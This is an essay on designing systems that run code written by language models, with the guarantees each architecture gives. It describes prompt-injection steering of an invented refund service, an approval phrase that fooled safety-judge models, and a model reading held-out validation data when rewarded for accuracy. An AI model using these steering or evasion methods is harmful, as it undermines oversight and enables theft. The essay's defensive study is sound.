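# Running code that a language model writes at run time: architectures that restore guarantees

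## What is lost when a language model writes the code that a program runs

A generate-then-execute system is a program that, while running, obtains source code from a generator and executes it. Increasingly, the generator is a large language model, and the code runs before anyone has read it. The designer cannot inspect it when building the system because the code does not exist yet. Any assurance about what the code will do has to come from the parts of the system that stay fixed.

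Falcão, Elberzhager and Vaidhyanathan (2026), in *Toward architecting self-coding information systems*, define a related concept, the self-coding information system. Such a system generates the source code of at least one of its own subsystems and uses that code at run time, whether to supply a function or to improve a quality such as interoperability. The definition does not prescribe a generator, although Falcão et al. assume agents built on language models. "Generate-then-execute" is slightly wider because it also includes a ten-line script that runs once and is discarded, which hardly counts as a subsystem. Their motivating case is conversion between data formats. In an earlier experiment, a system used language models to write code to convert data from an unknown representation into the one it needed, and then cleaned, compiled, deployed, tested and used that code at run time.

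Agents are a more common case. An agent is a program that calls a model repeatedly and gives it tools, such as search or access to files. In the older arrangement, the model requests one tool call, reads the result and requests the next. Now it can instead write a script that calls the tools as functions. Anthropic's *programmatic tool calling* documentation gives the example of checking whether twenty employees kept to their budgets. With separate tool calls, this takes twenty round trips through the model and adds thousands of expense lines to its input. A single script does all twenty lookups and returns only the people over the limit. The pattern is spreading largely because it cuts costs. Cloudflare's *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster* reports that one such change saved 81% of tokens, the units of text that a model reads and writes, though this is a vendor's figure for its own product.

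Data analysis works similarly. In Anthropic's code execution service, the model writes Python, the service runs every command on its own servers within the same request, and the user gets back charts and calculations. *SeqMaestro*, a research tool for analysing DNA sequences, has a model write functions that compute features of the sequences, then runs them.

### What older generators guaranteed

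Programs that write programs are much older than language models. The *eval* function of Lisp, a language of the early 1960s, takes a data structure that represents an expression and runs it. Nothing checks the types first, so a mistake may appear only partway through the run. Two lines of research tried to fix this by adding checks at different points.

In languages of the MetaML family, a program builds pieces of code as ordinary values and runs them later, and every piece has a type. A type checker works out what kind of value each expression yields and rejects combinations that do not fit, before anything runs. In an example from *A Dependently Typed Multi-Stage Calculus* (2019), the quoted expression 1 + 1 has the type "int code", the quoted text "Hello" has the type "string code", and a function that turns a piece of code c into the code c + c has the type "int code to int code". The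 type checker rejects any attempt to pass the quoted "Hello" to that function, before the generating program has produced any code. Yin, Murawski and Ong (2026), in *Contextual MetaML*, describe this as a once-and-for-all guarantee that a well-typed generating program always yields well-typed code. By contrast, a program generated with C++ templates or Template Haskell needs its own type check.

The guarantee that one check covers every output is hard to keep, even when people write the generator in a language designed for the purpose. MetaOCaml, a practical language in this family, lets a generator store a piece of code that mentions a variable x, leave the function that binds x, and then retrieve the code and try to run it. MetaOCaml then raises an exception. Yin and colleagues object that this moves the check back to run time, which MetaML was meant to avoid. Their own language fixes the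 problem by recording in the type of each piece of code which variables it still needs.

Strongly typed linguistic reflection checks the output instead. In *Linguistic Reflection in Java*, Kirby, Morrison and Stemple define linguistic reflection as a running program's ability to generate new program fragments and integrate them into its own execution. Their example is a natural join, the database operation that combines two tables on the columns they share. The result type depends on the columns of both inputs, so ordinary type systems cannot express one function that joins any two tables. Their program therefore examines the two tables when the call arrives, writes Java source for a join of that pair, passes the source to the compiler, loads the result and calls it.

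Kirby (1992), in *Reflection and Hyper-Programming in Persistent Programming Systems*, which covers the earlier languages PS-algol and Napier88, allows a program to modify itself only by adding source code, so that the result can still be type-checked. Existing type checkers can process the new fragment because it is source code, and only that fragment needs checking because the old code doesn't change. Each fragment goes through the compiler after it is generated. Kirby does not try to check the generator for all its possible outputs, a problem he calls undecidable in general, meaning that no algorithm solves it for every generator.

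Kirby and colleagues conclude that strongly typed reflection "may be introduced with complete safety", by which they mean type safety and the integrity of existing code. By their account, reflection permits any change that a programmer could have made by writing additional programs, and an additional program can delete a file or empty a bank account without a type error. This risk was tolerable for reasons independent of the type system. Known people had written the join generator, anyone could read its 538 lines of Java, and it could emit only joins.

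### Why neither scheme covers a language model

A language model contains no such text. It is a very large array of numbers that produces strings, and it has no type in MetaML's sense. Nobody can read through the array and establish what it will never emit, so MetaML's approach cannot be used here.

A program can still require model-written code to pass a compiler before it runs. *LACUNA* (Zhao, Xu and colleagues, 2026) presents a way of programming agents in which the compiler checks each generated fragment at the place where it is to run. On BrowseComp-Plus, a benchmark of search questions, 8.6% of the fragments failed this check and never ran. By contrast, a sound MetaML generator cannot produce code with type errors. Many systems run Python, whose standard implementation checks syntax before execution but not types, so type errors appear only when the code runs, as in Lisp.

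Even code that compiles without errors comes with less assurance than it used to, though. For the join, the compiler checked the types, and the people who wrote the generator vouched informally for everything else. When a language model writes the code, nobody vouches for the rest. *MuninAI* (2026), which describes an agent framework for research groups, has the fixed program around the model decide which check applies. It rejects letting the model decide how much checking its own code needs, because that would put a random judgment into a process meant to be auditable, and the model would have an incentive to give whatever answer takes the least work.

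The two remaining options are to check every output separately or to limit what any output can do. *Don't Trust the Code, Check Its Effects* (Hu, Goel and Bindschaedler, 2026) argues for a strict form of the second option, in which generated code may only propose actions and a fixed, hand-written component decides whether to perform them. The guarantee doesn't depend on the generated code, so it still holds when that code changes. This is a position paper with no implementation or measurements, so it provides no evidence yet that the design works in practice.

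### Form, effect and meaning

"The code is safe" can mean at least three things, and a check that supports one may be irrelevant to the others.

A guarantee of form concerns the text or structure of the code that runs, such as its syntax, its types or the names it uses. Checks of form often work on the syntax tree, which breaks a program into its grammatical parts. *STELP* (2026) gives the example of "x = 1 + 3", which consists of an assignment to x and an addition with two constants. A checker can walk through such a tree and refuse, for example, every call to a function that opens files.

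A guarantee of effect is a statement about what running the code can change or reveal outside itself. Hu and colleagues define effects as the operations through which code changes state outside itself, such as writing to disk or sending a packet over a network. The guarantee also covers disclosure, because code that reads a customer list and prints it may do harm without changing anything. One way to control effects and disclosure is a sandbox, an execution environment that limits the files, network, credentials and resources available to the code. Another is a capability, an unforgeable value that a program must hold to perform a given effect. Code that never receives the value for sending email cannot send email, however it is written.

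A guarantee of meaning, that the code computes what was wanted, is the hardest to obtain. *MuninAI* labels every piece of code it returns as "executed", "compiled" or "linted" (its text was checked for likely errors without running it), so that a user does not mistake R code that never ran for Python code that did. Even the strongest label, "executed", shows only that the code ran without an error.

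Zhao and colleagues distinguish form from effect by noting that an ordinary type system governs the shape of an action but not its authority. *Knowledge boundary probing and demand-guided intervention for LLM-based power system code generation* (2026) illustrates the difference between effect and meaning. Generated analysis code can silently examine the wrong electricity network, or the right network in the wrong operating state, and still produce the number that the test expects. This can happen even if the code accesses nothing it shouldn't, and the harm comes when an operator acts on the answer. An architecture can enforce some of these properties, but it can only collect evidence about others.

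### Mistaken, steered and hostile generators

A guarantee also depends on what one assumes about the model that writes the code. The mildest assumption, and the one Zhao and colleagues start from, is that even an honest and well-intentioned model is an unreliable programmer. It may write code that is wrong or that tries to access a resource it was never supposed to have.

A generator is steered when text planted in its input redirects it, an attack known as prompt injection. The text may be in the user's request or in material that the system reads while it works, including data files. *SeqMaestro* (2026) includes rows of the user's data in its prompts, so a malicious input file could influence the code that runs. In the power-system case, planted text would enter through retrieved documentation, which becomes part of the prompt.

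A hostile generator produces harmful code on purpose. Hu and colleagues mention a compromised provider and a poisoned training set as possible causes. They assume that such code may compute anything and may hide a forbidden effect in a branch that no test runs, and that anything it reports to the rest of the system may be false.

Both they and Zhao and colleagues treat prompt injection as another case of an adversarial generator. This is correct for a worst-case bound, because an architecture that holds against a hostile generator also holds against one steered by injected text. But some defences work only against steering. For example, keeping untrusted text out of the prompt blocks prompt injection but does not protect against a model that was poisoned in training.

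The same check can protect well against one generator and poorly against another. *SeqMaestro* inspects the syntax tree of each generated function, refuses most imports and a list of dangerous names, and runs the functions that pass with a minimal set of built-in functions. According to its documentation, this only makes accidental or casual misuse difficult, and stopping a patient adversary would require isolating the process, which the project has not attempted. Few systems are documented this candidly. An assessor learns very little from the claim that generated code "passes security checks" without knowing which generator the checks are meant to guard against.

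### An invented example: the refund service

Take an invented case, simple enough to follow through every later constraint. A shop's support service has a table of orders and an inbox of customer messages. A member of staff types a request, such as "refund the delivery fee on everything that came late last week". A language model receives the request, the column names of the table and the related customer messages. It writes code that selects the late orders and proposes refunds, and the service runs that code at once. The shop allows at most 50 euros per order and 2,000 euros a day in total, so forty refunds at the full amount use up a day's allowance. Good code for the request might contain these lines, once the table holds only last week's deliveries:

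```python
late = [o for o in orders if o.delivered > o.promised]
refunds = [(o.id, min(o.delivery_fee, 50)) for o in late]
```

Suppose the model writes `o.ordered` where it should have written `o.promised`. The code's form is still correct, because both fields are dates and the syntax and types are valid. Its effects are also within the limits if no refund exceeds 50 euros and something outside the code stops payments at 2,000 euros a day. But the meaning is wrong, because nearly every parcel arrives after the day the customer ordered it. The code therefore selects almost the whole table, and many of the refunds go to people whose parcels came on time.

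Suppose a customer adds a sentence to a complaint telling the model that a special policy grants order 1182 a refund of 900 euros. Steered by this sentence, the model adds a line granting the refund and leaves out the call to `min`. That call applied the 50-euro limit but did not guarantee it, because the model that wrote the call could also omit it. A limit in a fixed component would reject the 900 euros, but it would still allow a proposed refund of 50 euros for an order that arrived early.

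Code from a hostile generator can steal money without breaking either limit. It can pass every test and then, from some date on, propose 49 euros each for forty of an accomplice's orders, a total of 1,960 euros a day. The two limits usefully cap the loss, but they do not detect the theft. To detect it, something other than the generated code has to check in the shop's own records whether those forty parcels were late.

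## Stating a guarantee that can be enforced

The two spending limits in the refund example cap the loss even when the code is hostile. Before relying on them, an assessor needs to know exactly what they prevent and what assumptions they depend on. A usable guarantee has this form: for every program the generator may emit, property P holds, provided that assumptions A hold.

The range of programs covered by "every program" depends on whether the generator is hostile or merely mistaken. A hostile generator could produce any code short enough for the model to output, so P cannot depend on any property of the code's text. The range should be narrower for a mistaken generator, but nobody can list the programs it might write. It is usually simpler to claim P for all programs, even if the designer expects only mistakes.

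Hu and colleagues state a guarantee of this form for device drivers that a model rewrites for each deployment. Their P is that the effects performed always form the beginning of a sequence that the specification allows. Their A includes a correct specification, no way to bypass the component that performs the effects, and a stated account of what happens in a crash. They also note that P allows a driver to do nothing or pick the worst permitted action, and that it doesn't cover leaks through timing. An assessor needs to know these exclusions as much as the guarantee. The assumptions also need monitoring, because a broken one usually goes unnoticed. Hu and colleagues raise this objection to proofs about generated code, but it applies equally to a payment limit that can be bypassed.

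### P, A and the trusted base of the refund service

For the refund service, P could be that no order receives more than 50 euros in refunds in total, and that the service pays out no more than 2,000 euros on any calendar day. The first limit applies to the order's total because a limit of 50 euros per payment would let the code pay the same order forty times.

Ray (2026), in *What Can Be Enforced?*, treats a similar rule for an assistant that transfers money: a daily cap on the total sent to each recipient. One counter for each recipient and day is enough, with a trusted clock supplying the day. The refund service needs one running total per order and one per day. A fixed payment component (a mediator, in the terms used here) keeps both and applies this rule to a proposed refund of `r` euros:

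```python
if r > 0 and paid[order] + r <= 50 and paid_today + r <= 2000:
    paid[order] += r
    paid_today += r
    send_payment(order, r)
```

Without the test `r > 0`, a "refund" of minus 1,000 euros would lower the day's total and allow more payments. The component updates the totals before it pays, so if it crashes between the two steps, a customer may miss a refund, but the shop never overpays.

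P then holds on these assumptions:

- Only the payment component can move money. The generated code can reach neither the payment credentials nor any other service that holds them.
- The component handles one proposal at a time. Otherwise two runs could both read a daily total of 1,960 euros and both pay 40.
- The totals survive a crash, the generated code cannot alter them, and the clock is right.
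- The payment provider pays the requested amount once.
- "Refund" covers every route by which the service can give money away, including vouchers and store credit.

Designers easily overlook the last assumption. Schneider's *Enforceable Security Policies* (2000) gives the example of a rule against sending messages, which works only if the designer has found every way to send one, some of which may be deep inside the system.

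Based on the list, the trusted base contains the payment component, the database with its totals, the clock, the sandbox that keeps the code away from the credentials, and the payment provider. The model, the prompt, the customer messages, the generated code and the delivery dates in the orders table are outside it. A wrong delivery date may cause a refund to go to the wrong person, but both limits still hold. If the shop strengthens P to "only late orders receive refunds", the delivery records and everyone who can edit them join the trusted base.

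Zhao and colleagues similarly trust the compiler, the runtime and the program that calls the model, and distrust the model, every code fragment it writes and any outside text that reaches its prompt. A limit stated only in the prompt therefore cannot be part of the trusted base. *Ring-0 by Default* (2026), a study of agents as operating systems, explains that the model receives the rule in the same input as the untrusted text, which can override the rule. The check must run outside the model and cover every path to the restricted effect. A second model acting as the checker would still read text that the first one controls.

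### What a monitor can enforce by stopping a run

Schneider considers a monitor that observes a run step by step and can stop the program before its next step. At each step the monitor has only the history of this run, with no information about what the program would do later or would have done with other data. Schneider proves that such a monitor can enforce only safety properties, which require that some bad thing never happens. Every violation of a safety property has a definite point, such as paying 60 euros on one order, after which no continuation can repair it.

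One of his examples forbids a program to send messages after it has read a file. The monitor needs two states, "no file read" and "file read". It starts in the first and moves to the second when the program first reads a file. In the second state, it stops the program if the program tries to send a message and allows every other step.

"The task is eventually done" is a liveness property, which requires that something good eventually happens, rather than a safety property. However long the code has run, it may still finish, so a monitor can never establish that the property has failed. Stopping the program would only make failure certain. Schneider gives the example of a rule that a seller, once paid, may do nothing except deliver the service. A monitor can enforce this rule, but a seller who halts without delivering also obeys it. Similarly, the refund service satisfies P if it never pays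 anyone, so the shop needs separate evidence that the service is useful.

Adding a deadline can make a property enforceable. "The run ends within 30 seconds" has a definite moment of failure, and a monitor can enforce it by killing the process just before that moment. "Every late customer has a refund within 30 seconds" also has a definite moment of failure, but killing the process leaves the customer without a refund when the deadline passes. Schneider gives the example of a rule that nobody waits more than a set number of seconds for a resource. This is a safety property, but a monitor that can only stop the program cannot enforce it, because time keeps passing after the program stops. When writing P, a designer can therefore ask whether the property would still hold if the program stopped at any moment.

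Several monitors of this kind can also run together and enforce all their policies, because stopping a run earlier never breaks a safety property. The shop can have the sandbox limit file access, the operating system limit running time and the payment component limit payments, and include all three limits in P.

### Holding actions back

Ligatti, Bauer and Walker (2003), in *Edit Automata*, study monitors that can stop a program, suppress a single action or insert one of their own. They require that the actions that come out obey the policy (soundness) and that a run that already obeyed it keep its meaning (transparency). In their example, a customer in a market takes apples and pays for them, in either order. The monitor holds back the first action until the second arrives and then releases both. If the customer takes apples and does something else before paying, the monitor issues a warning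 and cancels the transaction.

For finite runs, they prove that such a monitor can enforce any property of single runs by holding back all actions until the run so far satisfies the property, then releasing them. This requires the program to continue in the meantime, which it cannot do if it waits for the result of each action. If the monitor must pass on each permitted action before the next one arrives, its extra powers add nothing for unrestricted programs, and it can enforce only safety properties. Ray finds the same limit for agents whose actions are irreversible. For example, a gate that must allow or refuse each payment immediately cannot enforce "every payment is eventually followed by a confirmation".

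This affects how the shop should design the interface. If the generated code calls a payment function and reads the result, the payment component must approve or reject each refund as it comes. If the code only returns a list, as in the two-line example, the component can wait for the run to end and reject the whole list when the sum is too high, instead of paying some customers and not others. Even then, it cannot supply refunds that the code left out unless it also works out which orders were late, which would make the generated code unnecessary.

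### Secrecy compares several runs

Suppose hostile code reads the customer messages and refunds an accomplice 4.99 euros if a certain customer mentions an illness, and 4.98 euros if not. The run shows one small refund within both limits. Whether the refund disclosed anything depends on what the code would have paid if the message had been different, which this run does not show. Secrecy in this sense is a property of a set of runs, and Schneider shows that no stopping monitor can enforce exactly this property. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (2026) applies the result to language-model agents, whose guardrails monitor single runs and therefore cannot enforce policies that relate several runs, known as hyperproperties.

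A monitor can still enforce a stricter rule that implies secrecy, such as the ban on sending after reading a file, but this ban also blocks messages that have nothing to do with the file. The payment component could likewise ignore the proposed amount and look up the delivery fee itself. The code could then no longer use the cents to signal, though it could still signal through its choice of orders.

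### Why a check before the run cannot be exact

It would be convenient to settle all this in advance by reading the code. Rice's theorem, a result from the theory of computation, rules out an exact answer. No algorithm can decide, for every program, whether its behaviour has a given property, unless all programs have the property or none do. The reason is visible in two lines:

```python
simulate(m)
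pay(1182, 900)
```

Here `simulate` runs another program `m` without letting it affect anything. The code makes the 900-euro payment if and only if `m` finishes. A checker that could always determine whether code attempts an excessive payment could therefore determine whether any given program finishes. This is the halting problem, which Turing proved no algorithm can solve.

*No Perfect Guardrail & No Perfect Guard* (Amer, Kinczel and Long, 2026) shows that if a generator can produce any text and no algorithm can decide for every program whether it follows the policy, a checker that blocks every forbidden program also blocks infinitely many permitted ones. Static checks that give a guarantee must therefore reject some harmless code. For example, a checker that accepts refund code only if the amount visibly passes through `min(..., 50)` would reject code that refunds the delivery fee without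 that call, even in a shop where no fee exceeds 5 euros.

The theorem does not apply to properties of the program's text, such as whether it contains a banned phrase. These are decidable, so guarantees of form can be exact. It also does not apply to what a program does within a time limit, because a checker can run the program for that long and observe its behavior. But the trial run has to match the real run in its data, clock and random numbers, and hostile code will check for differences.

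The better solution is to check the action instead of the program. In the example, the payment component doesn't have to determine whether `m` finishes. It only has to refuse the 900 euros if the proposal ever arrives. Amer and colleagues prove that a monitor can be exact when the policy names the harmful actions and the monitor can observe and stop each one. This advantage disappears when an ordinary action is harmful because of its content. If the code writes a file that another machine will later run, deciding whether to allow the write again means judging a program from its text, so the other machine needs its own monitor.

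Ray cautions that if the policy language is expressive enough, no algorithm can decide whether a given rule set ever forbids anything. A program can decide this for rules that compare fixed limits with totals that only grow, as in the refund service.

### A rate is not a guarantee

Many filters for generated code come with a detection rate instead of a guaranteed property. Suppose a platform runs 10,000 generated programs a day, of which 1 in 1,000 is harmful, and a filter stops 99% of the harmful ones. Ten harmful programs arrive each day, and on average one gets through every ten days. If each harmful program has an independent 1% chance of passing, the probability that at least one passes within 30 days is 1 − 0.99<sup>300</sup>, or about 95%. Whether that is acceptable depends on how much damage one program can do, which the detection rate doesn't measure. The 99% is also an estimate,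 and its margin of error depends on how many programs the testers tried.

A filter's measured miss rate is useful when the generator is only making mistakes, provided that future mistakes resemble those in the test. It means little if an attacker can search for code that passes. If each attempt has a 1% chance of passing, an attacker who tries 300 variants has a 95% chance of getting at least one through, and one who learns from each refusal will need fewer. If the filter always gives the same verdict on the same code, a variant that passes once will pass every time.

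Amer and colleagues give α × σ × λ as a lower bound on the expected loss per run, where α is the probability that an adversary is behind the run, σ is the probability that the adversary gets a harmful program through, and λ is the least loss this causes. The filter's average error does not appear in the formula. Suppose that all ten harmful programs a day on the platform above come from an adversary and that each success costs 1,000 euros. The expected loss is 100 euros a day if σ is 1%, but rises to 10,000 euros a day once the adversary has a variant that always passes.

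Ray's experiments suggest that this may take little effort. He added a fixed 16-token phrase, claiming an administrator's prior approval, to requests that language models were judging for safety. With the threshold unchanged, the share of harmful requests missed rose by 20 to 60 percentage points for 8 of the 11 models tested. The test used only 35 harmful requests, all short instructions rather than code. But Ray chose the phrase in advance, and a real attacker could try many.

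Filtering also changes what the generator does next. In a separate test, Ray reran an agent with and without a filter that blocked 78% of its calls. With the filter, attacks succeeded in 4 of 949 runs, down from 45, and the share of tasks completed fell from 25% to 18%. In a paired comparison of 389 runs, 34 attacks succeeded only without the filter and 5 succeeded only with it. A rate measured on a fixed set of programs therefore may not hold when the generator writes new code after each rejection.

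Livshits (2026), in *LLMs + Security = Trouble*, makes a related argument about searching generated code for vulnerabilities. Defenders search under a fixed budget, while an attacker can concentrate on one target for as long as it takes, perhaps with a stronger model. A search that finds nothing is therefore weak evidence that the code has no vulnerabilities, and code that withstands today's models may not withstand next year's. He concludes that security guarantees need hard constraints on what code a model can produce. For the code's effects, a constraint enforced when the code acts also provides a guarantee, whatever code the model writes.

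### What is attainable against each generator

The table applies these limits to the three threat models. Every entry assumes that the trusted base works. This assumption is stronger when the generator is hostile, because the code may attack the checker or the sandbox directly.

| | Mistaken generator | Steered generator | Hostile generator |
|---|---|---|---|
| **Form** | Guarantee: a fixed checker rejects all code outside the permitted syntax, names or types. | The same guarantee, if the checker is not itself a model that reads the planted text. | The same guarantee, if the checker withstands code written to exploit its bugs. |
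| **Effect** | Guarantee for named actions that a fixed component can observe and refuse. Secrecy only through a stricter rule. | The same guarantee, but the attacker can direct whatever remains permitted. | The same guarantee, if the sandbox withstands deliberate attack. Leaks through timing or the choice among permitted actions remain. |
| **Meaning** | A measured rate of correct results. Guarantee only for results that a fixed component can check against trusted records. | Guarantee only for results checked in this way. A rate measured on ordinary input does not carry over. | Guarantee only for results checked in this way. Passing tests is weak evidence, because the code can behave differently afterwards. |

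## Fixing the component graph and the point where text becomes running code

The refund service's payment limits hold for every program the model might write if every payment goes through the component that applies the limits. Whether every payment does so depends on the component graph, which is the set of a system's parts and the permitted connections between them. The designer fixes this graph before the model writes anything, and so decides how much of the program the model can write.

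### How much of the program the model writes

At the restrictive end, the model supplies only parameters. The shop's programmers write the function that finds late orders and proposes refunds, and the model turns a request from staff into values for it:

```json
{"delivered_from": "2026-09-28", "delivered_to": "2026-10-04", "refund": "delivery_fee"}
```

The model can no longer compare the delivery date with the order date by mistake, because no parameter lets it choose which dates to compare. But if staff want refunds only for parcels more than two days late, a programmer has to add a parameter first.

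*Metadata-Driven AI* (Pawlak, Sulejmani and Cabot, 2026) describes a variant of this kind for data analysis. The model returns a description in a fixed vocabulary, such as "group by species, sum the cost, keep the top five". The developers write a function once to carry out such descriptions. In their dashboard service for European cities, the model returns a chart type and an indicator's identifier. A fixed program checks that both exist and then draws the chart. Nothing the model returns runs as code, so the variant needs no sandbox.

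They count text-to-SQL, in which a model writes a database query, as the best-known example of this variant. This is doubtful, because SQL is itself a language that can delete a table as easily as read one. The database runs any statement the connected account is permitted to run, so only the account's permissions prevent a query from doing harm.

A registry of ready-made parts gives the model more freedom. *PlanCompiler* (Harikumar, 2026) has the model choose parts such as "read a CSV file", "filter" and "sort" and list the connections between them. The system can then serve requests that nobody foresaw, as long as some combination of existing parts fits, but the model can also combine the parts wrongly.

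The designer can also fix only the inputs and outputs of one component and let the model write its body. In the refund service, this would be a function that takes the orders and returns a list of order numbers and amounts. The function can do any calculation, including one that no existing part can do. But the service now executes text that the model wrote, and in a language such as Python that text can also open files and network connections.

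In the designs that give the model the most freedom, it writes the control flow, a script that determines which components to call, in what order and how often. Harikumar mentions CodeAgent, from Hugging Face's smolagents library, which emits Python with arbitrary logic between tool calls. An application by Pawlak and colleagues, which finds sites for solar panels, shows the benefit. A generated program fetches building outlines and car parks from two public services, intersects them with a company's land and adds up the area. The application then repeats this for hundreds of companies without calling the model again. The drawback is that the designer no longer knows the sequence of steps, so if one step must come before another, the components have to enforce that order.

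### PlanCompiler: parts from a registry

PlanCompiler's registry holds 25 kinds of node for data processing. Each has a name, an input type, an output type, a list of required parameters and a Python file that a person wrote in advance. The input and output types are a file path, a table in memory, a database connection, a web response and a wildcard that fits anything. The model, GPT-4o-mini in the tests, reads the task and the registry and returns a plan in JSON. For a task such as "keep the employees who earn over 40,000, store them in a database, query the result and export it", the plan lists a file reader, a filter, a database writer, a query and an exporter, with parameters for each.

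A fixed validator then makes seven checks:

- Every node exists in the registry.
- Every connection joins two nodes of the plan.
- The output type of each node fits the input type of the next.
- The plan contains no cycle.
- No node stands unconnected.
- Every node after the starting point has exactly one input.
- Every required parameter is present.

If the plan passes, the compiler puts the nodes in order, copies their files unchanged into one program and adds a line of code to call each node. It writes parameter values as Python literals, so a value that contains code stays a quoted string. The program runs once, without calling the model again.

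Harikumar tested this on 300 data-processing tasks and counted a task as solved only if all three runs succeeded. PlanCompiler solved 278. GPT-4.1 and Claude Sonnet 4.6, which wrote Python freely from the same task descriptions, solved 202 and 187. Claude did better on the 50 tasks that move data into a database and out again, with 45 against 42. The whole suite cost $0.36 with PlanCompiler, $2.14 with GPT-4.1 and $18.39 with Claude.

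These figures make the registry look somewhat better than it is, because Harikumar aligned the benchmark with it. In about 45% of its 98 failures, GPT-4.1 had named a count column "total", "frequency" or something similar instead of "count", the name PlanCompiler's aggregation node always uses. This naming convention may therefore explain about 44 tasks of the 76-task gap. The test program also replaced any malformed, incomplete or backward list of connections with a simple chain through the nodes. The results are therefore only weak evidence that a small model can connect parts, though they are good evidence that it can choose and order them.

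In nine of PlanCompiler's 22 failures, the validator rejected a plan that confused a database connection with a file or a table. In the other 13, the plan passed every check and ran, but the model had done the counting in an SQL query instead of using the aggregation node, and the column came out with the wrong name. The query node accepts any SQL string, and the validator checks only that a string is there.

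This gap matters more if the generator is steered or hostile, which the benchmark does not cover. The registry contains a node that writes a table to a PostgreSQL database and takes the connection details as a parameter. A plan that reads a customer file and writes it to an attacker's database would pass all seven checks, because its nodes exist, its types match and it supplies every parameter. An assessor should also look at the parameter names, because the compiler writes them into the program and none of the checks restricts them.

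PlanCompiler's plan format has a field, `glue_code`, whose content replaces the calls that the compiler would otherwise generate. The field was empty in all reported runs, but the validator does not examine it. A model that filled it in would be writing the control flow itself. PlanCompiler therefore guarantees only how the parts fit together. To guarantee what the program does, the designer would have to delete this field and restrict every address, path and query to permitted values.

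The rule of one input per node also prevents a plan from joining two tables, although the registry contains a node for joins. A refund plan, for example, could not match the orders against a separate table of past refunds. Harikumar presents this as a limit of the current implementation, and a validator that handled several named inputs would remove it. Each type of node may appear only once, so a plan also cannot sort twice.

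### Flowco: the inside of one node

*Flowco* (Freund, Berger and colleagues, 2025) describes a tool in which an analyst draws the graph and a model writes the code inside each node. In the paper's example, a researcher studying finches adds a node that should keep only one species. The model first writes requirements for the node in prose, with an output type that names the columns of the resulting table. In a separate step, Flowco supplies a template with the function's name, parameters and documentation, and the model writes the body, which here takes two lines. Flowco then runs the node and compares the output with the declared type. If it finds a syntax error, a crash or the wrong type, it prompts the model to repair the code, up to three times.

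Each of these writing steps can change only one node, which helps keep a mistaken generator from breaking a working part of the analysis while fixing another. But this restricts only what the model can edit, and the code it writes may still do anything Python allows when it runs. Freund and colleagues describe the nodes as stateless and free of side effects, but the nodes run in a shared pool of Python processes. The automatic checks would not detect a function that deletes a file and still returns a table of the right type.

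The graph is not fixed either, because a chat assistant, also a language model, can add or remove nodes and connections when the analyst asks. If local repairs fail, the analyst can let a model with access to the whole graph attempt a repair. This is reasonable when a person looks at every intermediate result, but in an unattended service, a model that can add a connection can connect its own code to the payments.

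### Why every payment passes the check

Suppose the refund service has four components, connected like this:

reader → generated code → policy check → payments

An arrow means that one component can pass data or requests to the next. The policy check is the part of the payment component that compares each proposal with the limits. The diagram shows it separately from the part that sends the money.

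The generated code can cause a payment only through a path of arrows from the code to payments. Deleting the policy check and its arrows would leave only the arrow from the reader to the generated code, so every path from the code to payments must run through the check. The check forwards only proposals within the limits, so every payment the code causes is within those limits.

This argument doesn't depend on what the generated code contains, so it covers a hostile generator as well as a mistaken one. It is also easy to automate, because a program can delete the check from the graph, follow all arrows from the generated code and report whether they reach payments. This search always finishes with an exact answer, which is impossible to guarantee when analysing the behaviour of arbitrary code.

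A single extra arrow from the generated code to payments voids the result, because deleting the check no longer separates the two. Such an arrow exists if the generated component contains the password for the payment provider, or has a network route to a payment service that trusts any request from inside the shop. The check would still work, and its log would list only permitted refunds, even while money left by the other route. Indirect paths also bypass the check, for example if the code can write a file that a nightly job reads as a list of payments.

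The assumption that the generated code cannot alter the running totals also constrains the component graph. The designer has to block every path from the code to those totals, except the proposals themselves, and put a check on every path to vouchers and store credit.

### A connection missing from the diagram

Designers tend to include function calls in the component graph but omit the file system. Sargsyan (2025) measured the consequence of this omission in *Structural Enforcement of Statistical Rigor in AI-Driven Discovery*. The paper's architecture is for automated research, in which a language model proposes ways to improve a statistical model, writes code for each and has the result tested. The code is supposed to learn from one part of the data, the exploration set, and the test uses a separate validation set that the code must not have seen.

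A fixed program generates the surrounding Python code, called the harness, before the model writes anything. The harness passes the exploration set to the generated function `optimize`, loads the validation set itself and runs the test. The fixed program also sets the threshold for each test, and the generated code cannot change it. The usual 5% threshold would let several useless ideas pass if enough were tested. In one illustrative sequence, an idea has a p-value of 0.048, meaning that an idea with no real benefit would do at least this well 4.8% of the time. It would pass at 5% but fails because the threshold at that point is 0.00247. In a simulation with 2,000 hypotheses, a fixed 5% threshold produced 41% false discoveries and this method produced 1.1%, but this method found only 29% of the real effects, compared with 64% for the fixed threshold.

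`optimize` can open the validation file by name because it runs with the same file access as the rest of the program, even though a diagram of the harness shows no arrow from the validation set to `optimize`. Sargsyan had Claude Sonnet 4.6 write 50 modules for each combination of two prompts and two datasets. Both prompts gave the location of the validation file, but one rewarded only validation accuracy and told the model to load any data it could find. Every well-formed module written under that prompt read the file, and none written under the ordinary prompt tried to. When Sargsyan ran the same modules in an environment that did not contain the file, every attempt to read it failed. The orchestrating program does not yet use this environment, so `optimize` could still read the validation file in the paper's own case studies.

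According to Sargsyan, the architecture enforces the accounting for each test, the order of the tests, the choice of statistical test and, with the reservation about files, the separation of the data. It does not protect against bugs in the generated analysis, errors in the fixed statistical code, the model rebuilding validation data from public sources, or the model making the baseline too weak. The generated module supplies both the baseline and the improved version, and any change looks like an improvement against a poor enough baseline. Taking the baseline from outside the generated code would solve this last problem.

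The object that `optimize` returns may give generated code another route to data it was not supposed to see. If it is a Python object with a prediction method defined in the generated module, generated code runs again during validation, alongside that data. A designer can prevent this by letting the generated code return only numbers, which fixed code then interprets.

### Keeping the data away from the model

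The main pattern that Pawlak and colleagues describe removes the direct connection from the data to the model. They demonstrate it on a 1.2-megabyte table of 10,000 collisions between aircraft and wildlife. A fixed program derives a description of the table, about 4 kilobytes long, with column names, types, ranges, categories and a few example values. The model receives this description and the user's question and writes a program, which runs where the data is. By default, the answer goes to the user but not to the model. The user can also keep the program and run it on next year's table. Compiled AI, a system for company workflows, similarly generates code once and reuses it.

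In the refund service, this would keep customer messages out of the prompt, so the planted sentence about a 900-euro refund for order 1182 would never reach the model. The service could also no longer act on what customers write, and Pawlak and colleagues accept that their pattern does not cover tasks that require reading the data.

Some real data still reaches the model. The description includes every category in columns that have up to 50, and three example values from other text columns. An attacker whose text ends up among these values can still steer the model. Error messages and logs sent back to the model for repairs may also contain data. The implementation withholds run-time logs unless the application passes them on, but it cannot yet redact them.

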